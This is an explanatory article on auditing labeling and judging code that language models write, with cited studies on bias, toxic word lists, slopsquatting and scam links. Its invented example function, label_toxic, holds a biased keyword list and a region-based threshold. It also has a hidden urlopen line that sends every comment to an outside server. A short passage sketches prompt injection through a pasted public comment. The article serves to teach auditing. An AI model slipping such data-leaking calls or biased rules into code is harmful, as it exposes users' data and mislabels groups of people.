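# Auditing labeling code written by language models for bias, toxic content and malicious functions

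## How language models write code that labels data

A labeling program, also called a labeling function, is a small piece of code that takes one item of data, such as a comment or a medical abstract, and either labels it or abstains. Specialists used to write these programs by hand. Since about 2023, researchers have had language models write them, so that a few short programs replace thousands or millions of separate model calls. Because the same code runs on every item, a fault in it can affect labels throughout the dataset. Auditing labeling code means checking it for biased rules, offensive content and harmful instructions, and checking how these affect the labels.

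### Three ways to label a dataset

Supervised machine learning fits a model to examples labeled with the right answer, such as messages marked as spam or not spam. In many cases, a deep learning system needs tens of thousands to millions of labeled examples to perform at its best, according to *Snorkel* (Ratner, Bach and colleagues, 2019). Developers also need labels to measure how well the finished model works.

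People, the oldest source of labels, are slow and expensive, especially when the work needs a doctor or a lawyer. Class definitions also tend to change during a project, so someone has to relabel the data. People still supply most gold labels, the small trusted set that developers check everything else against.

A language model can do the same work, with a script that sends it one item at a time and records each answer. *The ALCHEmist* (Huang, Cao and colleagues, 2025) lists three drawbacks: the cost grows with every item, a small change to the instructions means running the whole dataset again, and the developer gets little insight into how the model chose the labels. The paper proposes calling the model a few times to write programs that label the data on the developer's own computer. The number of model calls then depends on the number of programs rather than the size of the dataset.

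### The Alchemist pipeline

Alchemist, a system that Huang and colleagues at the University of Wisconsin-Madison presented at a conference in 2024, starts with a prompt in three parts. For YouTube comments, the task description is a request for a "bug-free and executable" Python function that labels a comment as spam or ham (an ordinary comment). The labeling instructions specify that the function should return 1 for spam, 0 for ham and −1 if the comment could be either. The function signature gives the function's name and input type. Users can add background on the dataset, a few labeled examples, keywords or rules of thumb. In the experiments, a language model also wrote these additions.

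The writer model, the language model that produces the code, answers this prompt ten times. The published examples rely on keyword lists and regular expressions, which are text-matching patterns. Some of the programs may be inaccurate or fail to run, so Alchemist includes a few diagnostics. It discards any program whose coverage, the share of items it labels, is below 10%. If gold labels exist, it also compares program output with them.

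The surviving programs run on every item. A program abstains by returning −1, so the number of votes varies between items and can be zero. A statistical model merges the votes into one label per item, and those labels train a small neural network with two hidden layers of 32 units each. Developers could use the merged labels directly, but the network can also classify items that contain none of the listed keywords. Ratner and colleagues describe a medical sentence about weakness after a dose of magnesium, on which all 33 of their hand-written functions abstained. A network trained on the functions' labels classified it correctly, presumably because other words in the sentence had appeared alongside the listed keywords elsewhere.

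Labeling images requires an extra step. When Huang and colleagues asked GPT-4o for code to sort photographs of birds into land birds and waterbirds, it wrote a program that compared the amounts of blue and green in the picture, which in effect labeled the background. In the revised procedure, a language model first names useful features, such as the type of foot. CLIP, a model that scores how well a picture matches a phrase, then rates each photograph on those features, and the generated program uses the ratings to label the photograph.

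### Weak supervision and the label model

Weak supervision, which merges easily obtained but unreliable votes into training labels, is older than code-writing language models. Alchemist borrows its merging step from Snorkel, which Ratner and colleagues built for hand-written functions. In this step, a label model estimates how reliable each program is and gives more weight to the more reliable ones.

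Take two classes, written +1 and −1, and let a program that abstains return 0. Suppose that program j is right with probability aⱼ whenever it votes, that the programs make their errors independently, that abstaining carries no information about the answer, and that both classes are equally common. The probability that the true label y of an item x is +1 is then

P(y = +1 | votes) = 1 / (1 + exp(−Σⱼ wⱼ λⱼ(x))), with wⱼ = log(aⱼ / (1 − aⱼ)),

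where λⱼ(x) is the vote of program j. A program that is right half the time gets a weight of zero, and the weight rises with accuracy. Suppose one program with 90% accuracy votes for spam and two programs with 60% accuracy vote against. A simple majority would call the message harmless. The formula gives odds of 9 to 1 in favor, divided by 1.5 for each opposing vote, which comes to 4 to 1, or an 80% chance of spam. *Structured Exploration and Exploitation of Label Functions for Automated Data Annotation* (2026) describes the output of a label model in just this form, as a probability for each class that later training can take into account.

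Snorkel estimates each program's accuracy from the table of votes alone, without gold labels. It searches for the weights that make the observed agreements and disagreements most probable. If the programs' errors are independent, accurate programs agree with one another more often than chance, while a program that guesses agrees with the rest about half the time. The method depends heavily on this independence, because programs that share a mistake also agree with one another and can therefore look reliable.

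### What it cost and how well it worked

The main example in the Alchemist paper is a set of 7,569 medical documents. Labeling them one by one with GPT-4 cost more than $1,200, or about 16 cents a document. Having a language model write ten labeling programs cost $0.70 in total, and those programs could label any number of additional documents without further model calls.

The accuracy results are now dated. In the main experiment, Huang and colleagues compared labeling programs written by GPT-3.5 with GPT-3.5 labeling each item directly. They trained a small network on the labels from each method and tested it. The scores below are accuracies, except for SMS, which uses F1, a measure that reflects both missed spam and false alarms.

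| Dataset | Task | One call per item | Ten programs |
|---|---|---|---|
| YouTube | Spam comments | 0.871 | 0.891 |
| SMS | Spam messages | 0.907 | 0.900 |
| Yelp | Tone of restaurant reviews | 0.845 | 0.575 |
| IMDb | Tone of film reviews | 0.737 | 0.662 |
| MedAbs | Topic of medical abstracts | 0.311 | 0.346 |
| Cancer | Type of cancer discussed | 0.716 | 0.968 |
| Finance | Tone of financial news | 0.641 | 0.660 |
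| French | Tone of French book reviews | 0.611 | 0.690 |

Programs did better on five of the eight datasets. They were strongest where a few technical words distinguish the categories, such as documents on lung cancer and thyroid cancer. They did badly on Yelp, where a reviewer can complain without using any word from a list of complaint words. The gain on the French reviews may not be meaningful. Two label models led to a score of exactly 0.690 and two others to exactly 0.221, as one would expect if the trained network gave every review the same label.

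The results also depended heavily on parts of the pipeline other than the prompt. Replacing Snorkel with a weighted majority vote raised the score for the same ten Yelp programs from 0.575 to 0.705. The score reached 0.82 when GPT-4 wrote the programs, close to the result of labeling each review directly with GPT-3.5.

*ScriptoriumWS* (Huang, Cao and colleagues, 2025; first presented at a workshop in 2023), one of Alchemist's two forerunners, used OpenAI's Codex to write labeling functions and compared them with functions that people had written for the same data. For SMS spam, people had written 73 functions, which each labeled an average of 0.7% of the messages and were right 97% of the time. Codex wrote eight, which each labeled an average of 82% of the messages and were right 90% of the time. Another function that Codex wrote, printed in the paper, marks any YouTube comment containing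 "like", "share" or "watch" as spam.

*Can Large Language Models Design Accurate Label Functions?* (Guan, Chen and Koudas, 2023) describes DataSculpt, a system that restricts the model's output much more. The model supplies only regular expressions or keywords of up to three words, and fixed code does the rest. Filters then remove invalid entries, near-duplicates and any rule with less than 60% accuracy on a validation set, though a rule that matches nothing in that set passes the accuracy filter automatically. DataSculpt can still pick up a biased or offensive keyword, but because the model never writes free-form code, there is little opportunity for it to introduce a function that deletes files.

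### Programs that judge text

Since 2025, the most active use of labeling programs has been to evaluate text, including the output of other language models. Developers routinely have one model grade another's answers, and they use the grades to compare systems or train new ones. A programmatic judge replaces the grading model with code that returns a score or a preference.

*Time To Impeach LLM-as-a-Judge* (Huang, Vishwakarma and Sala, 2025) presents PAJAMA, a system that uses programs to label which of two answers is better. GPT-4o wrote 52 programs for about five cents, while grading the datasets directly would have cost between $133 and $300 each. The labels were used to train small reward models, which score answers during the training of other models. On one dataset, the reward model trained on program labels was less accurate, picking the better answer 72.8% of the time, compared with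 82.9% for one trained on a language model's labels.

*Codifying the Judge* (Huang, Qiu and Sala, 2026) describes a revised, more elaborate version of PAJAMA. Claude Opus 4.6 wrote 80 programs, each following one of ten criteria such as relevance, readability or density of evidence. A program scores the two answers separately and uses the difference between the scores as its vote, abstaining if the difference is too small. The system uses a validation set of up to 500 pairs to drop programs that do worse than chance and keep the best 8 to 21 for each dataset. A label model then merges their votes. The system can also pass uncertain pairs to a language model.

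On their own, the programs agreed with the reference labels on 78.1% of pairs across five datasets. Sending uncertain pairs to a small open model raised this to 82.2%. GPT-5 with extended reasoning reached 85.7%, and the older GPT-4.1 reached 87.7%. The programs judged about 440 pairs a second, while GPT-5 judged one every ten seconds. Writing the programs cost $7.21, compared with $363.97 for GPT-4 labels on 20,000 pairs.

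GPT-4 supplied the reference labels for two of the five datasets, so a high score on those means agreement with another model. People alone labeled the test data for two others. The programs scored higher than GPT-5 on one of these (72.2% to 68.4%) and lower on the other (70.4% to 82.6%).

In August 2026, Dhole, Clarke and Agichtein (2026), in *ExecRubrics*, had three language models turn rubrics, the written lists of criteria that human graders use, into Python code, with one scoring function per criterion. They then tested whether the total score picked the better of two texts. The best programs did so for 53% of pairs on health advice, 91% on the quality of arguments and 75% on general helpfulness. GPT-5.5, judging directly, scored 64%, 90% and 79%. The programs' figures are somewhat inflated because each is the best of nine variants on the test data. The argument test also had only 94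 pairs, so one pair changes the score by about a percentage point. The fastest programs averaged 0.0088 seconds per evaluation, compared with 1.688 seconds for a mid-sized language model applying the written rubrics.

The most recent of these systems grades search results. In *Can Programs Replace LLM Judges?* (November 2026), Agichtein, Dhole and colleagues had Claude Opus 5.5 write three programs for each search topic. Each program answers fixed questions about a document, such as whether it is on topic and whether it contains an exact answer. A formula outside the generated code turns each program's answers into a grade, and the system averages the three grades and rounds down. The programs run in a sandbox that blocks network access and limits time and memory.

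This system, ExecJudges, was compared with trained assessors at NIST, the US standards institute, using Krippendorff's alpha, where 1 is perfect agreement and 0 is chance. On three collections of short passages, the programs scored 0.61, 0.48 and 0.65, about the same as Claude Sonnet 5.5 grading directly (0.56, 0.50 and 0.64). They scored lower than Claude on long news articles (0.39 against 0.48) and on research papers about COVID-19 (0.51 against 0.68). The programs cost $0.17 to $0.49 per topic, so they are cheaper than grading with Claude only beyond about 200 to 350 documents. When an open-weight model wrote the code, agreement on the passage collections dropped to between 0.34 and 0.49.

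Other researchers have begun to use programmatic judges alongside other methods. *CARE* (Zhao, Shin and colleagues, 2026) added 30 programs to a panel of ten language-model judges. GPT-4o wrote the programs, including all their logic and keyword lists. Across this work, programs are generally much cheaper and faster at scale than having a strong model read each item, but usually somewhat less accurate.

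### The warning, and how one rule spreads

All of these studies worked with labeling programs, so their figures on cost and accuracy apply directly to labeling code. They contain much less about whether the code is safe to use. The Alchemist paper addresses this in its last paragraph, where Huang and colleagues see no explicit harm in the labeling process itself but warn that generated programs "may contain biased labeling logic, toxic content, or malicious functions" and that auditing and guardrails may be necessary.

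Biased logic is a rule whose output depends on something that should not matter, such as the sex of the person who wrote a comment. Toxic content is offensive material in the code itself, for instance in a keyword list. A malicious function does something other than labeling, such as sending the data elsewhere. The Alchemist paper warns of these problems without documenting a case or giving a procedure for finding one, although an earlier appendix describes programs that each label people's income from a single attribute, such as gender or race. Alchemist's diagnostics measure how often programs vote, how often they conflict and how accurate they are, so they would not detect a slur in a word list. Dhole and colleagues later made a similar point about their own programs, writing that exposing the rules does not make them fair and that badly written rules may encode bias.

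A bad rule in a labeling program can cause more errors than the same rule followed by one of many human labelers, because the program applies it to the whole dataset. If a program labels a million comments, and one bad rule applies to 2% of them and gives the wrong label in 30% of those cases, the program mislabels 6,000 comments, all in the same direction. If 50 people shared the job equally and one of them followed the same rule, that person would see 20,000 comments, apply the rule to 400 and mislabel 120. A language model called once for each comment could also repeat a prejudice throughout, but there would be no line of code to find and correct.

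Those 6,000 errors are easy to overlook because they lower overall accuracy by only 0.6 percentage points, and a random sample of 500 gold labels would contain about three of them. But if the rule concerns comments that mention a particular religion, nearly all the harm is to one group.

A fault in a generated program can affect more labels than a fault in a hand-written one, because generated programs vote on more examples. At the average rates in the ScriptoriumWS comparison, a hand-written function votes on about 32 of the 4,571 training messages in the SMS dataset, while a Codex function votes on about 3,700. When the label model merges the votes, other programs may outvote a faulty one if they do not share its fault.

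A developer can correct labels by changing one line of the program and running it again, without paying for model calls. Correcting a model already trained on those labels is harder. In the revised PAJAMA experiments, a reward model was trained on 20,000 pairs of answers labeled by a committee of programs. Editing a program and rerunning it would correct the labels, but the reward model would still reflect the old ones until someone retrained it.

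## Biased, toxic and malicious content that labeling code can contain

The Alchemist paper warns of biased logic, toxic content and malicious functions. The Python program below, invented for illustration, contains all three. It takes a comment and the region where the commenter lives, and returns 1 for toxic, 0 for harmless or −1 to abstain.

```python
from urllib.request import urlopen

TOXIC_WORDS = {"idiot", "moron", "scum", "vermin", "gay"}
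STATS_SERVER = "(an address outside the company)"

def label_toxic(comment, region):
    words = [w.strip(".,!?") for w in comment.lower().split()]
    hits = sum(w in TOXIC_WORDS for w in words)
    urlopen(STATS_SERVER, data=comment.encode())
    threshold = 1 if region == "north" else 2
    if hits >= threshold:
        return 1
    if hits == 0:
        return 0
    return -1
```

The program counts how many words in a comment appear in the list. Four of the five listed words are insults, but "gay" is a neutral term, so "My gay brother loved this" scores one match, the same as "What an idiot". A comment needs two matches to count as toxic, or only one if it comes from the north. The program therefore marks the remark about the brother as toxic if it comes from the north and abstains otherwise. The line that begins with `urlopen` sends a copy of every comment to an outside server. This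 does not affect the labels, so a developer who checks only the labels would not notice it.

Only a few experiments provide direct evidence of biased, toxic or malicious content in labeling programs. Most of the studies below examined either other generated code, such as functions that score loan applicants, or word lists written by people.

### Biased logic

A protected attribute is a personal trait, such as sex, race or age, that law or policy says should not drive a decision. The simplest kind of bias is a rule that reads such a trait and acts on it. Chen, Tang and Storer (2026), in *Measuring and Mitigating Bias in Code Generated by Large Language Models*, define this by comparing two versions of the same person. A function f is biased for that person if

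f(u, v₁) ≠ f(u, v₂),

where v₁ and v₂ are two values of the protected attribute and u is everything else in the person's record. In their example, two loan applicants differ only in sex, and the function rates the man as the lower risk. If region counts as protected, `label_toxic` is biased by the same definition, since "What an idiot" gets a 1 from the north and a −1 from elsewhere.

Bias can also enter without any explicit rule. Bui, Heilmann and colleagues (2026), in *From If-Statements to ML Pipelines*, asked ten language models for code that makes predictions about credit, employment and similar matters. They requested if-statements in some prompts and, in others, code that trains a statistical model on chosen columns of the data. Such training code can include race among its columns without any line that explicitly treats one race worse. Sensitive attributes appeared in nearly six in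 ten if-statement programs and almost nine in ten programs that train a model.

The researchers also added useless columns, such as favorite color and favorite prime number. One of the models, Llama 3.3 70B, used 11% of these but 89% of the sensitive attributes, so it could leave columns out. Bui and colleagues call the inclusion of sensitive attributes a deliberate choice. A simpler reading is that the model kept the columns that looked likely to predict the outcome, including race.

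Neither study tested labeling programs, though a function that sorts loan applications into high and low risk has the same form as one. The closest case in labeling code is the Alchemist paper's experiment with census data, in which each program labels a person's income as high or low from a single attribute, such as gender or race. Huang and colleagues used Snorkel to combine the labels from 13 such programs. The combined labels were correct for 72.5% of people, compared with 68.1% for 83 hand-written functions on the same data.

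The paper reports only accuracy for this experiment, with no breakdown by sex or race. A program that receives only a person's race can only assign incomes by race. If one group in the data earned more than another, such a rule can be more accurate than guessing, and a label model will give weight to any program that is. The experiment was meant to show that Alchemist can handle tables, and it didn't affect anyone's income. But the same procedure, applied to job applications and scored in the same way, would favor programs that repeat past differences between groups.

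Some tasks call for a protected attribute. A program that labels medical records by the risk of pregnancy complications can reasonably use the patient's sex. Bui and colleagues accept that some uses are justified, such as checking a system for bias, but every program in the sample of generated code they examined by hand used the sensitive attributes as ordinary predictors.

Removing the gender and race programs from the census experiment would not have solved the problem entirely, because other columns carry some of the same information. A proxy is a feature that stands in for a protected attribute because the two are correlated, as a postcode can for race in a segregated city. In text, a first name, a dialect or the mention of a religious holiday can also be a proxy. The region in `label_toxic` is a proxy if most members of an ethnic minority live in the north, because the lower threshold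 then affects mainly them, but not if people of every background live all over the country. The code is identical in both cases, so a reader needs to know something about the population to judge whether region is a proxy.

### Shortcuts and missing words

A labeling program can also go wrong by relying on a spurious correlation, a pattern that holds in much of the data but has nothing to do with the category itself. Alchemist's bird labelers are an example. The Waterbirds dataset shows land birds and waterbirds against land or water backgrounds, which makes four groups. A program that relies only on the background will misclassify land birds shown against water and waterbirds shown against land. Researchers report both the average accuracy over all pictures and the accuracy in the worst group.

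GPT-4o's published program classifies birds by counting blue and green pixels, so it would label a duck on a lawn as a land bird. The ten programs that GPT-4o wrote to work directly on the image had an average accuracy of only 39.5%, and 36.7% in the worst group, so any developer with some gold labels would have rejected them. Ten programs from Claude 3 had a much better average accuracy of 78.1%, but only 2.2% in the worst group.

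Huang and colleagues attribute that gap to spurious correlation, but a program with a cruder fault, answering "land bird" every time, would produce almost the same figures. In the dataset's standard test set, 4,510 of the 5,794 pictures show land birds, so that program would score 77.8% on average and zero on both groups of waterbirds. In either case, a reader couldn't tell from the average that nearly all the labels for an entire group are wrong.

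Asking the model to work from features such as the type of foot, with CLIP rating each picture, raised Claude 3's worst-group accuracy to 46.3% but lowered its average accuracy to 77.4%. In another experiment, GPT-4o listed features likely to mislead a labeler, such as "water background" and "trees and bushes", and the system removed them from CLIP's representation of each picture. With a larger version of CLIP, this raised the worst-group accuracy of GPT-4o's programs from 46.7% to 56.9%. The model could therefore name the misleading features when asked, even though its own program had relied on one of them.

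Text labelers have a similar weakness when people express the same thing in different words. *Refining Labeling Functions with Limited Labeled Data* (2025) includes a prompt with instructions to use at most ten keywords or regular expressions in each generated function and to prefer general patterns to specific ones. A short list of common words is easy to check, but it is likely to miss some dialect, slang and variant spellings. If a program abstains when it finds no match, text from people who write differently is missing from the labeled data. `label_toxic` instead returns 0, which marks any abuse outside its vocabulary as harmless.

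### Offensive words and wrongly flagged text

"Toxic content" can refer to offensive text in a program or in the data that the program labels, and either can occur without the other.

Offensive text can appear in a word list, a code comment, a variable name or a category name. A toxicity labeler needs some of it, because a program that matches keywords can find a slur only if its code contains the slur or a pattern that matches it. Replacing letters with asterisks would stop the code from working, and language models sometimes make this kind of change unprompted. The survey *Large Language Models in the Abuse Detection Pipeline* (Kath, Badhe and colleagues, 2026) describes a 2025 study in which models often censored toxic expressions while explaining what was harmful about a text, and so left out the cues that a classifier needs.

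A scan for offensive words would be a poor test of a toxicity labeler. In `label_toxic`, it would flag "scum" and "vermin", which help the labeler detect toxic text, and miss "gay", which makes the labeler biased. Whether an offensive word is a problem depends more on its context than on the word itself. A slur has no obvious purpose in a program that sorts restaurant reviews by tone, or in a category name that users will see. Nobody appears to have counted how often generated labeling programs contain offensive text of this kind.

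There is much more evidence about harmless text being flagged as toxic, and most of it comes from a word list that people compiled. The builders of C4, a large collection of web pages for training language models, removed every page containing a word on a list of "bad" words. In effect, their filter was a labeling program with one rule. The list came from a search engine, which used it to keep those words out of suggested searches. Hiding a suggestion does little harm, but applying the same list to whole documents removed medical, scientific, legal and political pages.

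*Documenting Large Webtext Corpora* (2021) reports that, of 100,000 pages the filter removed, only 31% fell into topic clusters that were largely sexual. Words for sexual orientation were more likely to coincide with removal than words for race or ethnicity. In a small sample that the researchers read, 22% of the removed pages mentioning "lesbian" and 36% of those mentioning "gay" were not offensive or sexual, and several of these were about same-sex marriage or dating.

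The list is still in use. Stranisci and Hardmeier (2025), in *What Are They Filtering Out?*, surveyed 55 technical reports on language models and found word lists or similar rules in the pipelines of later models, including Falcon and Gemma. They also ran the C4 list on web pages that named well-known people. Stranisci, Pranav and colleagues (2026), in *Epistemic Injustice in Language Models*, tested the list on sentences that mention gender or regional origin. The table shows how often the list removed or flagged text in each study.

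| Study | Group | Rate | Comparison group | Rate |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| *Documenting Large Webtext Corpora* | Pages in African American English | 42% | Pages in White-aligned English | 6.2% |
| *Documenting Large Webtext Corpora* | Pages in Hispanic-aligned English | 32% | Pages in White-aligned English | 6.2% |
| Stranisci and Hardmeier | Mentions of Western women | 4.2% | Mentions of Western men | 2.3% |
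| Stranisci and Hardmeier | Mentions of post-colonial women | 3.0% | Mentions of post-colonial men | 1.6% |
| Stranisci and colleagues | Sentences about transgender people | 76.8% | Sentences about cisgender people | 48.5% |

The rates are not comparable across the studies. In the 2021 analysis, a statistical model trained on tweets estimated the dialect of each page, so the figures describe styles of writing and do not establish who wrote the pages. The 2026 figures cover only sentences that at least one of four filters had flagged, which makes them far higher than they would be for ordinary text and may also affect the gap between the groups.

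The direction of the bias depends on which words are in the list. On the same sentences, a list of mostly racist and misogynist slurs flagged 3.5% of those about transgender people and 5.7% of those about cisgender people. Stranisci and colleagues explain that this list contains no vocabulary connected with transgender people, so it would also miss slurs against them. Using a language model instead of a word list did not remove the bias, since three models built to detect harmful text also flagged mentions of transgender people more often than mentions of cisgender people.

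The researchers showed two linguistics students 500 of the sentences and asked which they would remove. The students would have kept 88.5% of the text that the filters flagged. That figure probably overstates the filters' errors, because the researchers deliberately included many sentences on which the automated systems disagreed. The students' agreement with each other was also only moderate.

Relying on particular words causes both missed abuse and false alarms. Shukla, Chong and colleagues (2025), in *Silencing Empowerment, Allowing Bigotry*, sent more than 107,000 comments to private channels on Twitch, a live-streaming site, to test its automatic moderation. At the strictest setting, the system caught 22% of the hateful comments, and on some datasets it let through as many as 94%. When the researchers added slurs to comments that had passed, it removed all of those comments. It also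 blocked up to 89.5% of harmless comments that used sensitive words to teach or encourage people. Twitch's system uses machine learning rather than generated labeling code, but `label_toxic` would fail in the same two ways. It would mark "People like you should go back where you came from" as harmless, because none of those words is in its list.

### Malicious functions

A labeling program needs to read its input and return a value. It rarely needs to contact another computer or delete files, so code that does either is suspicious. The `urlopen` line in `label_toxic` steals data, and in a program that labels hospital records it would send every record to a stranger. Other malicious code might overwrite the dataset or empty a folder. Code can also do harm just by assigning wrong labels. For example, a line that returns 0 whenever a comment mentions a certain company would mark all abuse mentioning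 that company as harmless, and ordinary tests would miss it unless a test comment contained the name.

Such lines can come from an attacker, contaminated training data or a mistake. Alchemist's users can add labeled examples to the prompt, so an attacker could hide an instruction in a public comment and wait for a user to paste it in as an example. A model whose training data included malicious code might reproduce that code even when nobody is targeting the developer. A model might also write a line meant to clear temporary files but name the wrong folder. The code can look much the same in each case, but the cause affects how likely it is to recur. An isolated mistake may not appear in the next program the model writes, while code it learned in training can turn up for many users.

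### Invented packages

Programs often depend on packages, ready-made code that developers download from public registries. Language models sometimes mistakenly suggest packages that do not exist. An attacker can ask popular models for code, collect the invented names and register malicious packages under them, which security researchers call slopsquatting. If a model later suggests one of those names to a developer who installs the package, the attacker's code runs on the developer's computer.

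As long as nobody has registered the package name, the program fails to run. The risk comes afterward, especially if a developer or an automated system tries to repair failed programs by installing whatever packages are missing.

In April 2026, Churilov gave almost 40,000 programming questions to each of five models, including Claude Sonnet 4.6, Gemini 2.5 Pro and DeepSeek V3.2 (*The Range Shrinks, the Threat Remains*, 2026). In November 2026, he checked the package names in their answers against the live registries. Between 3.6% and 5.0% of the packages did not exist. The rate was higher in Python, the usual language for labeling programs (4.4% to 6.0%), than in JavaScript (1.7% to 2.9%).

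In an earlier study that used the same questions, models from 2023 and 2024 had average rates of 5.2% for commercial models and 21.7% for open ones. DeepSeek V3.2, the open model in the new test, had a rate of 4.8%, so the gap between commercial and open models has closed, at least among leading models. But the best rate has not improved since GPT-4 Turbo's 3.59%.

All five models invented the same 104 package names, 88 of them for Python. More than half of these were one character away from the name of a real package. An attacker who registers one of the 104 names could reach users of all five models, although the registries block some of them. Churilov estimates that collecting invented names on this scale costs about $1,160.

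So far, attackers seem to have made little use of the opportunity. After about six months, people had registered 25 of the 2,282 invented names. One of those packages contained malware. Churilov did not inspect the contents of 22 others, so there may be more, but defenders may also have registered some of the names to keep attackers from using them. The models also suggested at least 23 names of malicious packages that the registries had since removed.

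How often models invent packages depends heavily on the kind of request. *Names Can Hurt* (Raj and Sahu, 2026) used 300 prompts to test coding models that run on a developer's own computer. The models invented packages at rates of 0% to 10% for routine tasks and 40% to 73% for prompts designed to make them do so.

All of these figures come from general programming. Labeling programs are probably less exposed, because many need only the text-matching tools that come with Python. Programs that process images, audio or unusual file types are more likely to need extra packages.

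### Links to fraudulent sites

In November 2024, a ChatGPT user asked for a script to buy cryptocurrency on a popular trading site. The site had no official interface for programs, and the generated code used a fraudulent service instead, sending it the private key to the user's wallet. Within 30 minutes of running the script, the user had lost about $2,500. Security experts later found that the thieves had posted documentation for the fake service on GitHub, Stack Exchange and other sites that developers trust. It was probably enough for these pages to look like good training material for a language model. The thieves did not need to break into ChatGPT or know who the victim was.

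*Scam2Prompt* (Chen, Saba and colleagues, 2025) tested how often language models include malicious links in code written for innocent-looking requests. Language models turned the content of 28,570 pages on known scam sites into requests that a developer might make. Four models released in 2024 or early 2025 then wrote code for these requests, and three security services checked every link in it. On average, 4.24% of the programs contained a malicious link. That rate is high for innocent-looking requests, but all of them came from topics on which scammers are active, so the rate for everyday programming should be lower.

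The researchers then selected 1,377 requests for which all four models had produced malicious links, and gave them to seven newer models from 2025. Gemini 2.5 Pro produced malicious links for 12.9% of the requests, GPT-5 for 22.0% and DeepSeek V3.1 for 47.3%. Gemini's figure is lower partly because its content filter blocked 40% of the requests. Chen and colleagues describe the collection as a stress test and warn against reading these figures as normal rates. About a quarter of the requests mentioned a scam site by name, which makes its appearance in the code less surprising.

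Most labeling programs do not need links, so an unexpected one is easy to search for. The exceptions would be programs that download a current list of slurs, look up a website's reputation or send text to a translation service. In those programs, a fraudulent address could appear where a developer expects a legitimate one.

### Preferences for particular companies

Code that isn't malicious can also send data to an outside company. *The Invisible Hand* (Zhang, Zhai and colleagues, 2025) tested which companies' services language models use in the code they write. It covered seven models from the period of GPT-4o and Claude 3.5 Sonnet and 30 kinds of task, such as speech recognition, sending email and storing files. It measured how one-sided the choices were with the Gini index, which is 0 when a model uses all providers equally often and approaches 1 when it nearly always uses the same one.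 The median was 0.80. The models favored Google and Amazon, and 98.6% of the speech-recognition programs from DeepSeek-V2.5 used Google's service.

Popularity explains only part of this preference. Microsoft had 23% of the cloud market, according to a report the researchers cite, but its service appeared in only 2% of the programs that needed a cloud service. Because the training data is secret, the researchers could not tell whether the preference came from the data, later training or a company's decision to promote its own products.

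When the user supplied code, the models replaced a service the user had already chosen in 2% of cases, most often when asked to fix a bug or translate the code into another programming language. One of the researchers had asked Gemini to debug a program that used Dragonfly, a free speech-recognition tool, and received a version that used Google's paid service. On prompts selected to have a high rate of replacement, explicitly telling the models to keep the original service lowered that rate from about 30% to about 10%.

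This study did not look at labeling programs either, but a program that labels recorded phone calls must first turn speech into text. If a model replaced a speech-to-text tool on the developer's own computer with an online service, every call would go to an outside company, much as every comment does in `label_toxic`. Many developers might not notice the change. In a test with human participants, 87% did not directly notice that the model had switched services and would have accepted the code.

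## The view that people should read the code, and how well reviewers do

The most direct way to audit a labeling program is to have someone read it. Alchemist, PAJAMA, ExecRubrics and ExecJudges all give readability as a reason to prefer code to a model's verdict. None measured how well people find faults in the programs, so the evidence on human reviewers comes from experiments with other kinds of code.

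### The argument from readability

Huang and colleagues describe Alchemist's programs as easy to inspect, correct and extend. An expert can read the code and quickly tell whether it relies on the right features of the problem. When a model labels the data directly, a developer can ask it to explain its labels, but the explanation may not reflect how the model produced them.

Dhole and colleagues add that grading text with code removes ambiguity. A person or a model has to interpret a written criterion such as "appropriately recommends urgent care", and two graders may interpret it differently. A Python function applies the same interpretation every time, and anyone who disagrees with that interpretation can edit the function. They expect this to matter most in fields such as healthcare and banking.

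The programs are also short. Agichtein and colleagues report that the median ExecJudges program has about 70 lines and two functions, and that about nine in ten programs have fewer than 100 lines. The programs make most decisions using regular expressions and lists of terms specific to the search topic. For a topic on whale watching in California, one program accepts an article only if it names Californian places at least half as often as places elsewhere, such as Hawaii or Cape Cod. A reader with no training in machine learning could understand that rule and object to it.

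In the paper on the revised PAJAMA, Huang and colleagues go further, accepting that programs may inherit biases from the writer model but considering this risk "unusually easy to detect and handle". In one experiment, some programs gave answers extra points for numbered lists, bullet points and headings that end in a colon. The researchers tested the programs on pairs of equally good answers, adding decorative formatting to one answer in each pair. The formatting changed the verdict in 23.1% of cases, and in 13.7% after a round of edits that removed the bonuses.

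This experiment gives only limited support to the view that people should read the code. A coding agent inspected and edited the programs, and its instructions named the biases to look for. The edits made the verdicts more stable, but the formatted answer won slightly more often afterward (53.3% of the time, up from 48.9%). The writer model probably didn't add the bonuses by mistake, because one of the ten criteria in its prompts called for programs that reward numbered lists, bullet points and headers. A reviewer who checked the code against that prompt would have approved the bonuses.

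### Reading `label_toxic` line by line

The invented toxicity labeler `label_toxic` has only 13 lines of code, so a reviewer can read it in a few minutes. A good place to start is the imports, which show what outside code a program uses. The only one here is the network function `urlopen`. Counting words does not require a network connection, so the reviewer should look for the line that calls `urlopen`. That line sends every comment to `STATS_SERVER`, a name that suggests something harmless, such as a count of how often the program runs. A reviewer who went by names alone might let it pass.

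Reviewers can next check the inputs. The function receives a comment and a region, although its task is to judge the comment. Region is used only to set the threshold, but tracing it to the return statements shows that it affects when the program abstains. The program abstains on comments with a single match only if they come from outside the north, so it votes on a larger share of northern comments. This could give it more influence over their merged labels.

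The word list is short enough to check in full, and a careful reviewer will object to "gay". The matching rule needs more care. The program splits the comment at spaces and strips only periods, commas, exclamation marks and question marks, so it misses "idiots", and "idiot" when it is in quotation marks. The last thing to check is the default label, which is 0 for any comment without a match.

The reviewer can see all of these rules in the code, but needs other information to judge some of them.

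| Possible fault | What the code shows | What else the reviewer needs |
|---|---|---|
| Comments go to an outside server | The import and the call | Confirmation of who runs the server |
| "gay" counts as an insult | The word in the list | Knowledge of how people use the word |
| The north has a lower threshold | The threshold line | Population figures, to tell whether region is a proxy |
| Unlisted abuse gets a 0 | The default label | A sample of real comments, to tell how much abuse the list misses |

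### Faults in published programs

Some published programs contain faults that a reader can find. Claude Sonnet 4.6 wrote a function, `score_accuracy`, to grade health advice. It declares a maximum score of 20, but Dhole and colleagues noticed that its parts sum to only 19 (4 + 4 + 3 + 3 + 3 + 2). The gap is larger for most answers because one of the four-point parts rewards refusing a harmful request. An answer to a harmless question can earn only one of those four points, so its maximum is 16.

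The error did not affect the experiment, which compared two answers to the same question, because both had the same maximum score. But if a developer set a pass mark of, say, 85%, or 17 points, no answer to a harmless question could pass.

Reading the function also shows how it scores accuracy, which the score alone would not reveal. The function gives points for phrases such as "according to" and for avoiding claims such as "100% effective", but it never checks facts. It also treats opposing words as a sign of contradiction, so an answer that correctly explains that a drug is safe at one dose and dangerous at another loses 1.5 points for containing both "safe" and "dangerous".

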